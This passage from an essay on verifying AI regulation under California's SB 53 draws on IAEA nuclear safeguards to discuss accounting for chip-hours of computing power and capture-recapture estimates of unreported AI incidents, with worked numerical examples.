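Even with accurate measurements, the balance covers only the material and plants that a state has declared. Iraq had accepted IAEA inspections of its declared nuclear material, and the inspectors had reported no diversion. After the Gulf War in 1991, they discovered that Iraq had also been running a large secret programme to enrich uranium, partly at sites they had never visited. A balance for the declared plants could not have revealed this programme.

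From then on, the IAEA set out to verify that a state's declarations were complete as well as correct. It began using satellite images and intelligence from member states, and taking swabs of dust, since a few particles of enriched uranium can reveal an undeclared plant. States that accept the Model Additional Protocol of 1997 must also declare activities that involve no nuclear material, such as making centrifuge parts, and must let inspectors visit more places at short notice.

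Samples can also contradict a declaration about the past. In 1992, North Korea declared that it had separated a small amount of plutonium once, in 1990. The IAEA's analysis of samples indicated that it had done so several times over about three years. The inspectors knew the declaration was incomplete, but they could not tell how much plutonium it left out.

### Accounting for computing power

Of these methods, material accounting has attracted the most detailed proposals for AI. The specialised chips that large models need take the place of plutonium. In *What Does It Take to Catch a Chinchilla?* (2023), Shavit proposed a system with three parts. Chips would occasionally save a snapshot of the model they were working on. Developers would keep enough information about each training run to show inspectors where that model came from. Inspectors would track chip sales so that nobody could assemble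 a large undeclared stock.

The chips themselves can be counted much like plutonium, with purchases as receipts and resales as shipments. Their use needs a different balance, because an hour of computing cannot be stored. Suppose a company declares a data centre with 10,000 chips. Over 30 days they provide 7.2 million chip-hours:

| | Million chip-hours |
|---|---|
| Available | 7.2 |
| Declared training | 4.0 |
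| Serving customers and internal agents | 2.6 |
| Idle | 0.4 |
| Unexplained | 0.2 |

If each chip performs 4 × 10<sup>14</sup> useful operations a second, reaching SB 53's threshold of 10<sup>26</sup> operations takes about 69 million chip-hours. That would occupy the whole data centre for almost ten months. The unexplained 0.2 million chip-hours are 0.3 per cent of those 69 million, so a secret training run on that scale would leave a far larger gap over the year. An agent that breaks into another company in an afternoon uses too little computing to distinguish from measurement error.

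A developer could also record a forbidden training run as "serving customers", and the totals would still balance. That is why Shavit's inspectors need the snapshots. For undeclared data centres, they would need other evidence, as in Iraq. Chip sales matter most for this, along with electricity use and satellite images.

Such accounting could also help with SB 53, because computing power determines which developers the law covers. When California's Department of Technology recommends changes to the law's definitions, it must consider whether outsiders could verify who falls under them.

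### Two lists of incidents

Incidents have no opening and closing stock, but comparing lists kept separately by two parties can give an estimate of how many went unreported. Biologists developed this method to count animals. They marked the ones they caught, then checked how many marked ones turned up in a second catch. Chandra Sekar and Deming applied it to official records in *On a Method of Estimating Birth and Death Rates and the Extent of Registration* (1949), comparing a register of births and deaths near Calcutta with a house-to-house survey.

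Suppose developers have reported 60 incidents to the state, and a research group has collected 40 from victims and the press. The lists have 24 in common. The developers' list thus contains 24 of the researchers' 40, or 60 per cent. If it also contains 60 per cent of all incidents, there must be 100 in all:

*N* = (60 × 40) / 24 = 100

| | On the researchers' list | Not on it | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
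| On the developers' list | 24 | 36 | 60 |
| Not on it | 16 | 24 (estimated) | 40 |
| Total | 40 | 60 | 100 |

The two lists together contain 76 different incidents, so an estimated 24 are on neither. The number on both lists is also 24, but this is a coincidence. The estimate is rough because the lists are short, and the usual 95 per cent interval for the total is about 80 to 120.

The calculation assumes that the lists are independent, so an incident on one list is no more or less likely than any other to be on the second. If this is wrong, the estimate can be far off. The table below assumes that the true number of incidents is 100 and that the lists still contain 60 and 40.

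| In common | On at least one list | Estimated to be on neither | Really on neither |
|---|---|---|---|
| 12 | 88 | 112 | 12 |
| 24 | 76 | 24 | 24 |
| 32 | 68 | 7 | 32 |

The last row is the most likely for AI. A developer has more reason to report an incident once a newspaper has written about it, and the press is more likely to hear of a spectacular incident that the developer would have reported anyway. Both effects make the overlap too large and the estimate too low. The first row could apply if the researchers deliberately looked for incidents that developers had not reported.

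A mixture of conspicuous and quiet incidents has the same effect as the last row, even if neither list influences the other. If 100 conspicuous incidents each have a 90 per cent chance of getting on each list, and 100 quiet ones have a 10 per cent chance, each list will contain about 100 incidents, with about 82 in common. This gives an estimate of 122 instead of 200. To correct for this, Chandra Sekar and Deming made separate estimates for groups of similar cases. Here that gives (90 × 90) / 81 = 100 for the conspicuous incidents and (10 × 10) / 1 = 100 for the quiet ones, although the second estimate rests on a single match.

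Nobody seems to have made a detailed proposal to use this method for AI incidents. The second list could come from victims, from a public collection such as the AI Incident Database, or from reports that the public and whistleblowers send to the state. Both lists would have to cover the same period and use the same definition of an incident. Somebody would also have to recognise when two entries describe the same incident, because missed matches make the overlap look too small and the estimate too high.

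In California, outsiders can't do this matching, because developers' reports are confidential and the annual summary is anonymised. The Office of Emergency Services could, since it receives reports from both developers and the public. *Trust but Verify* (2026), a Carnegie Endowment report on implementing SB 53, says California will have to make sure the government gets enough information about serious incidents. Capture-recapture would first need a broader definition of an incident. Under the present definition, even the Hugging Face attack would appear on neither list, and the formula gives no estimate when the lists have no incidents in common.
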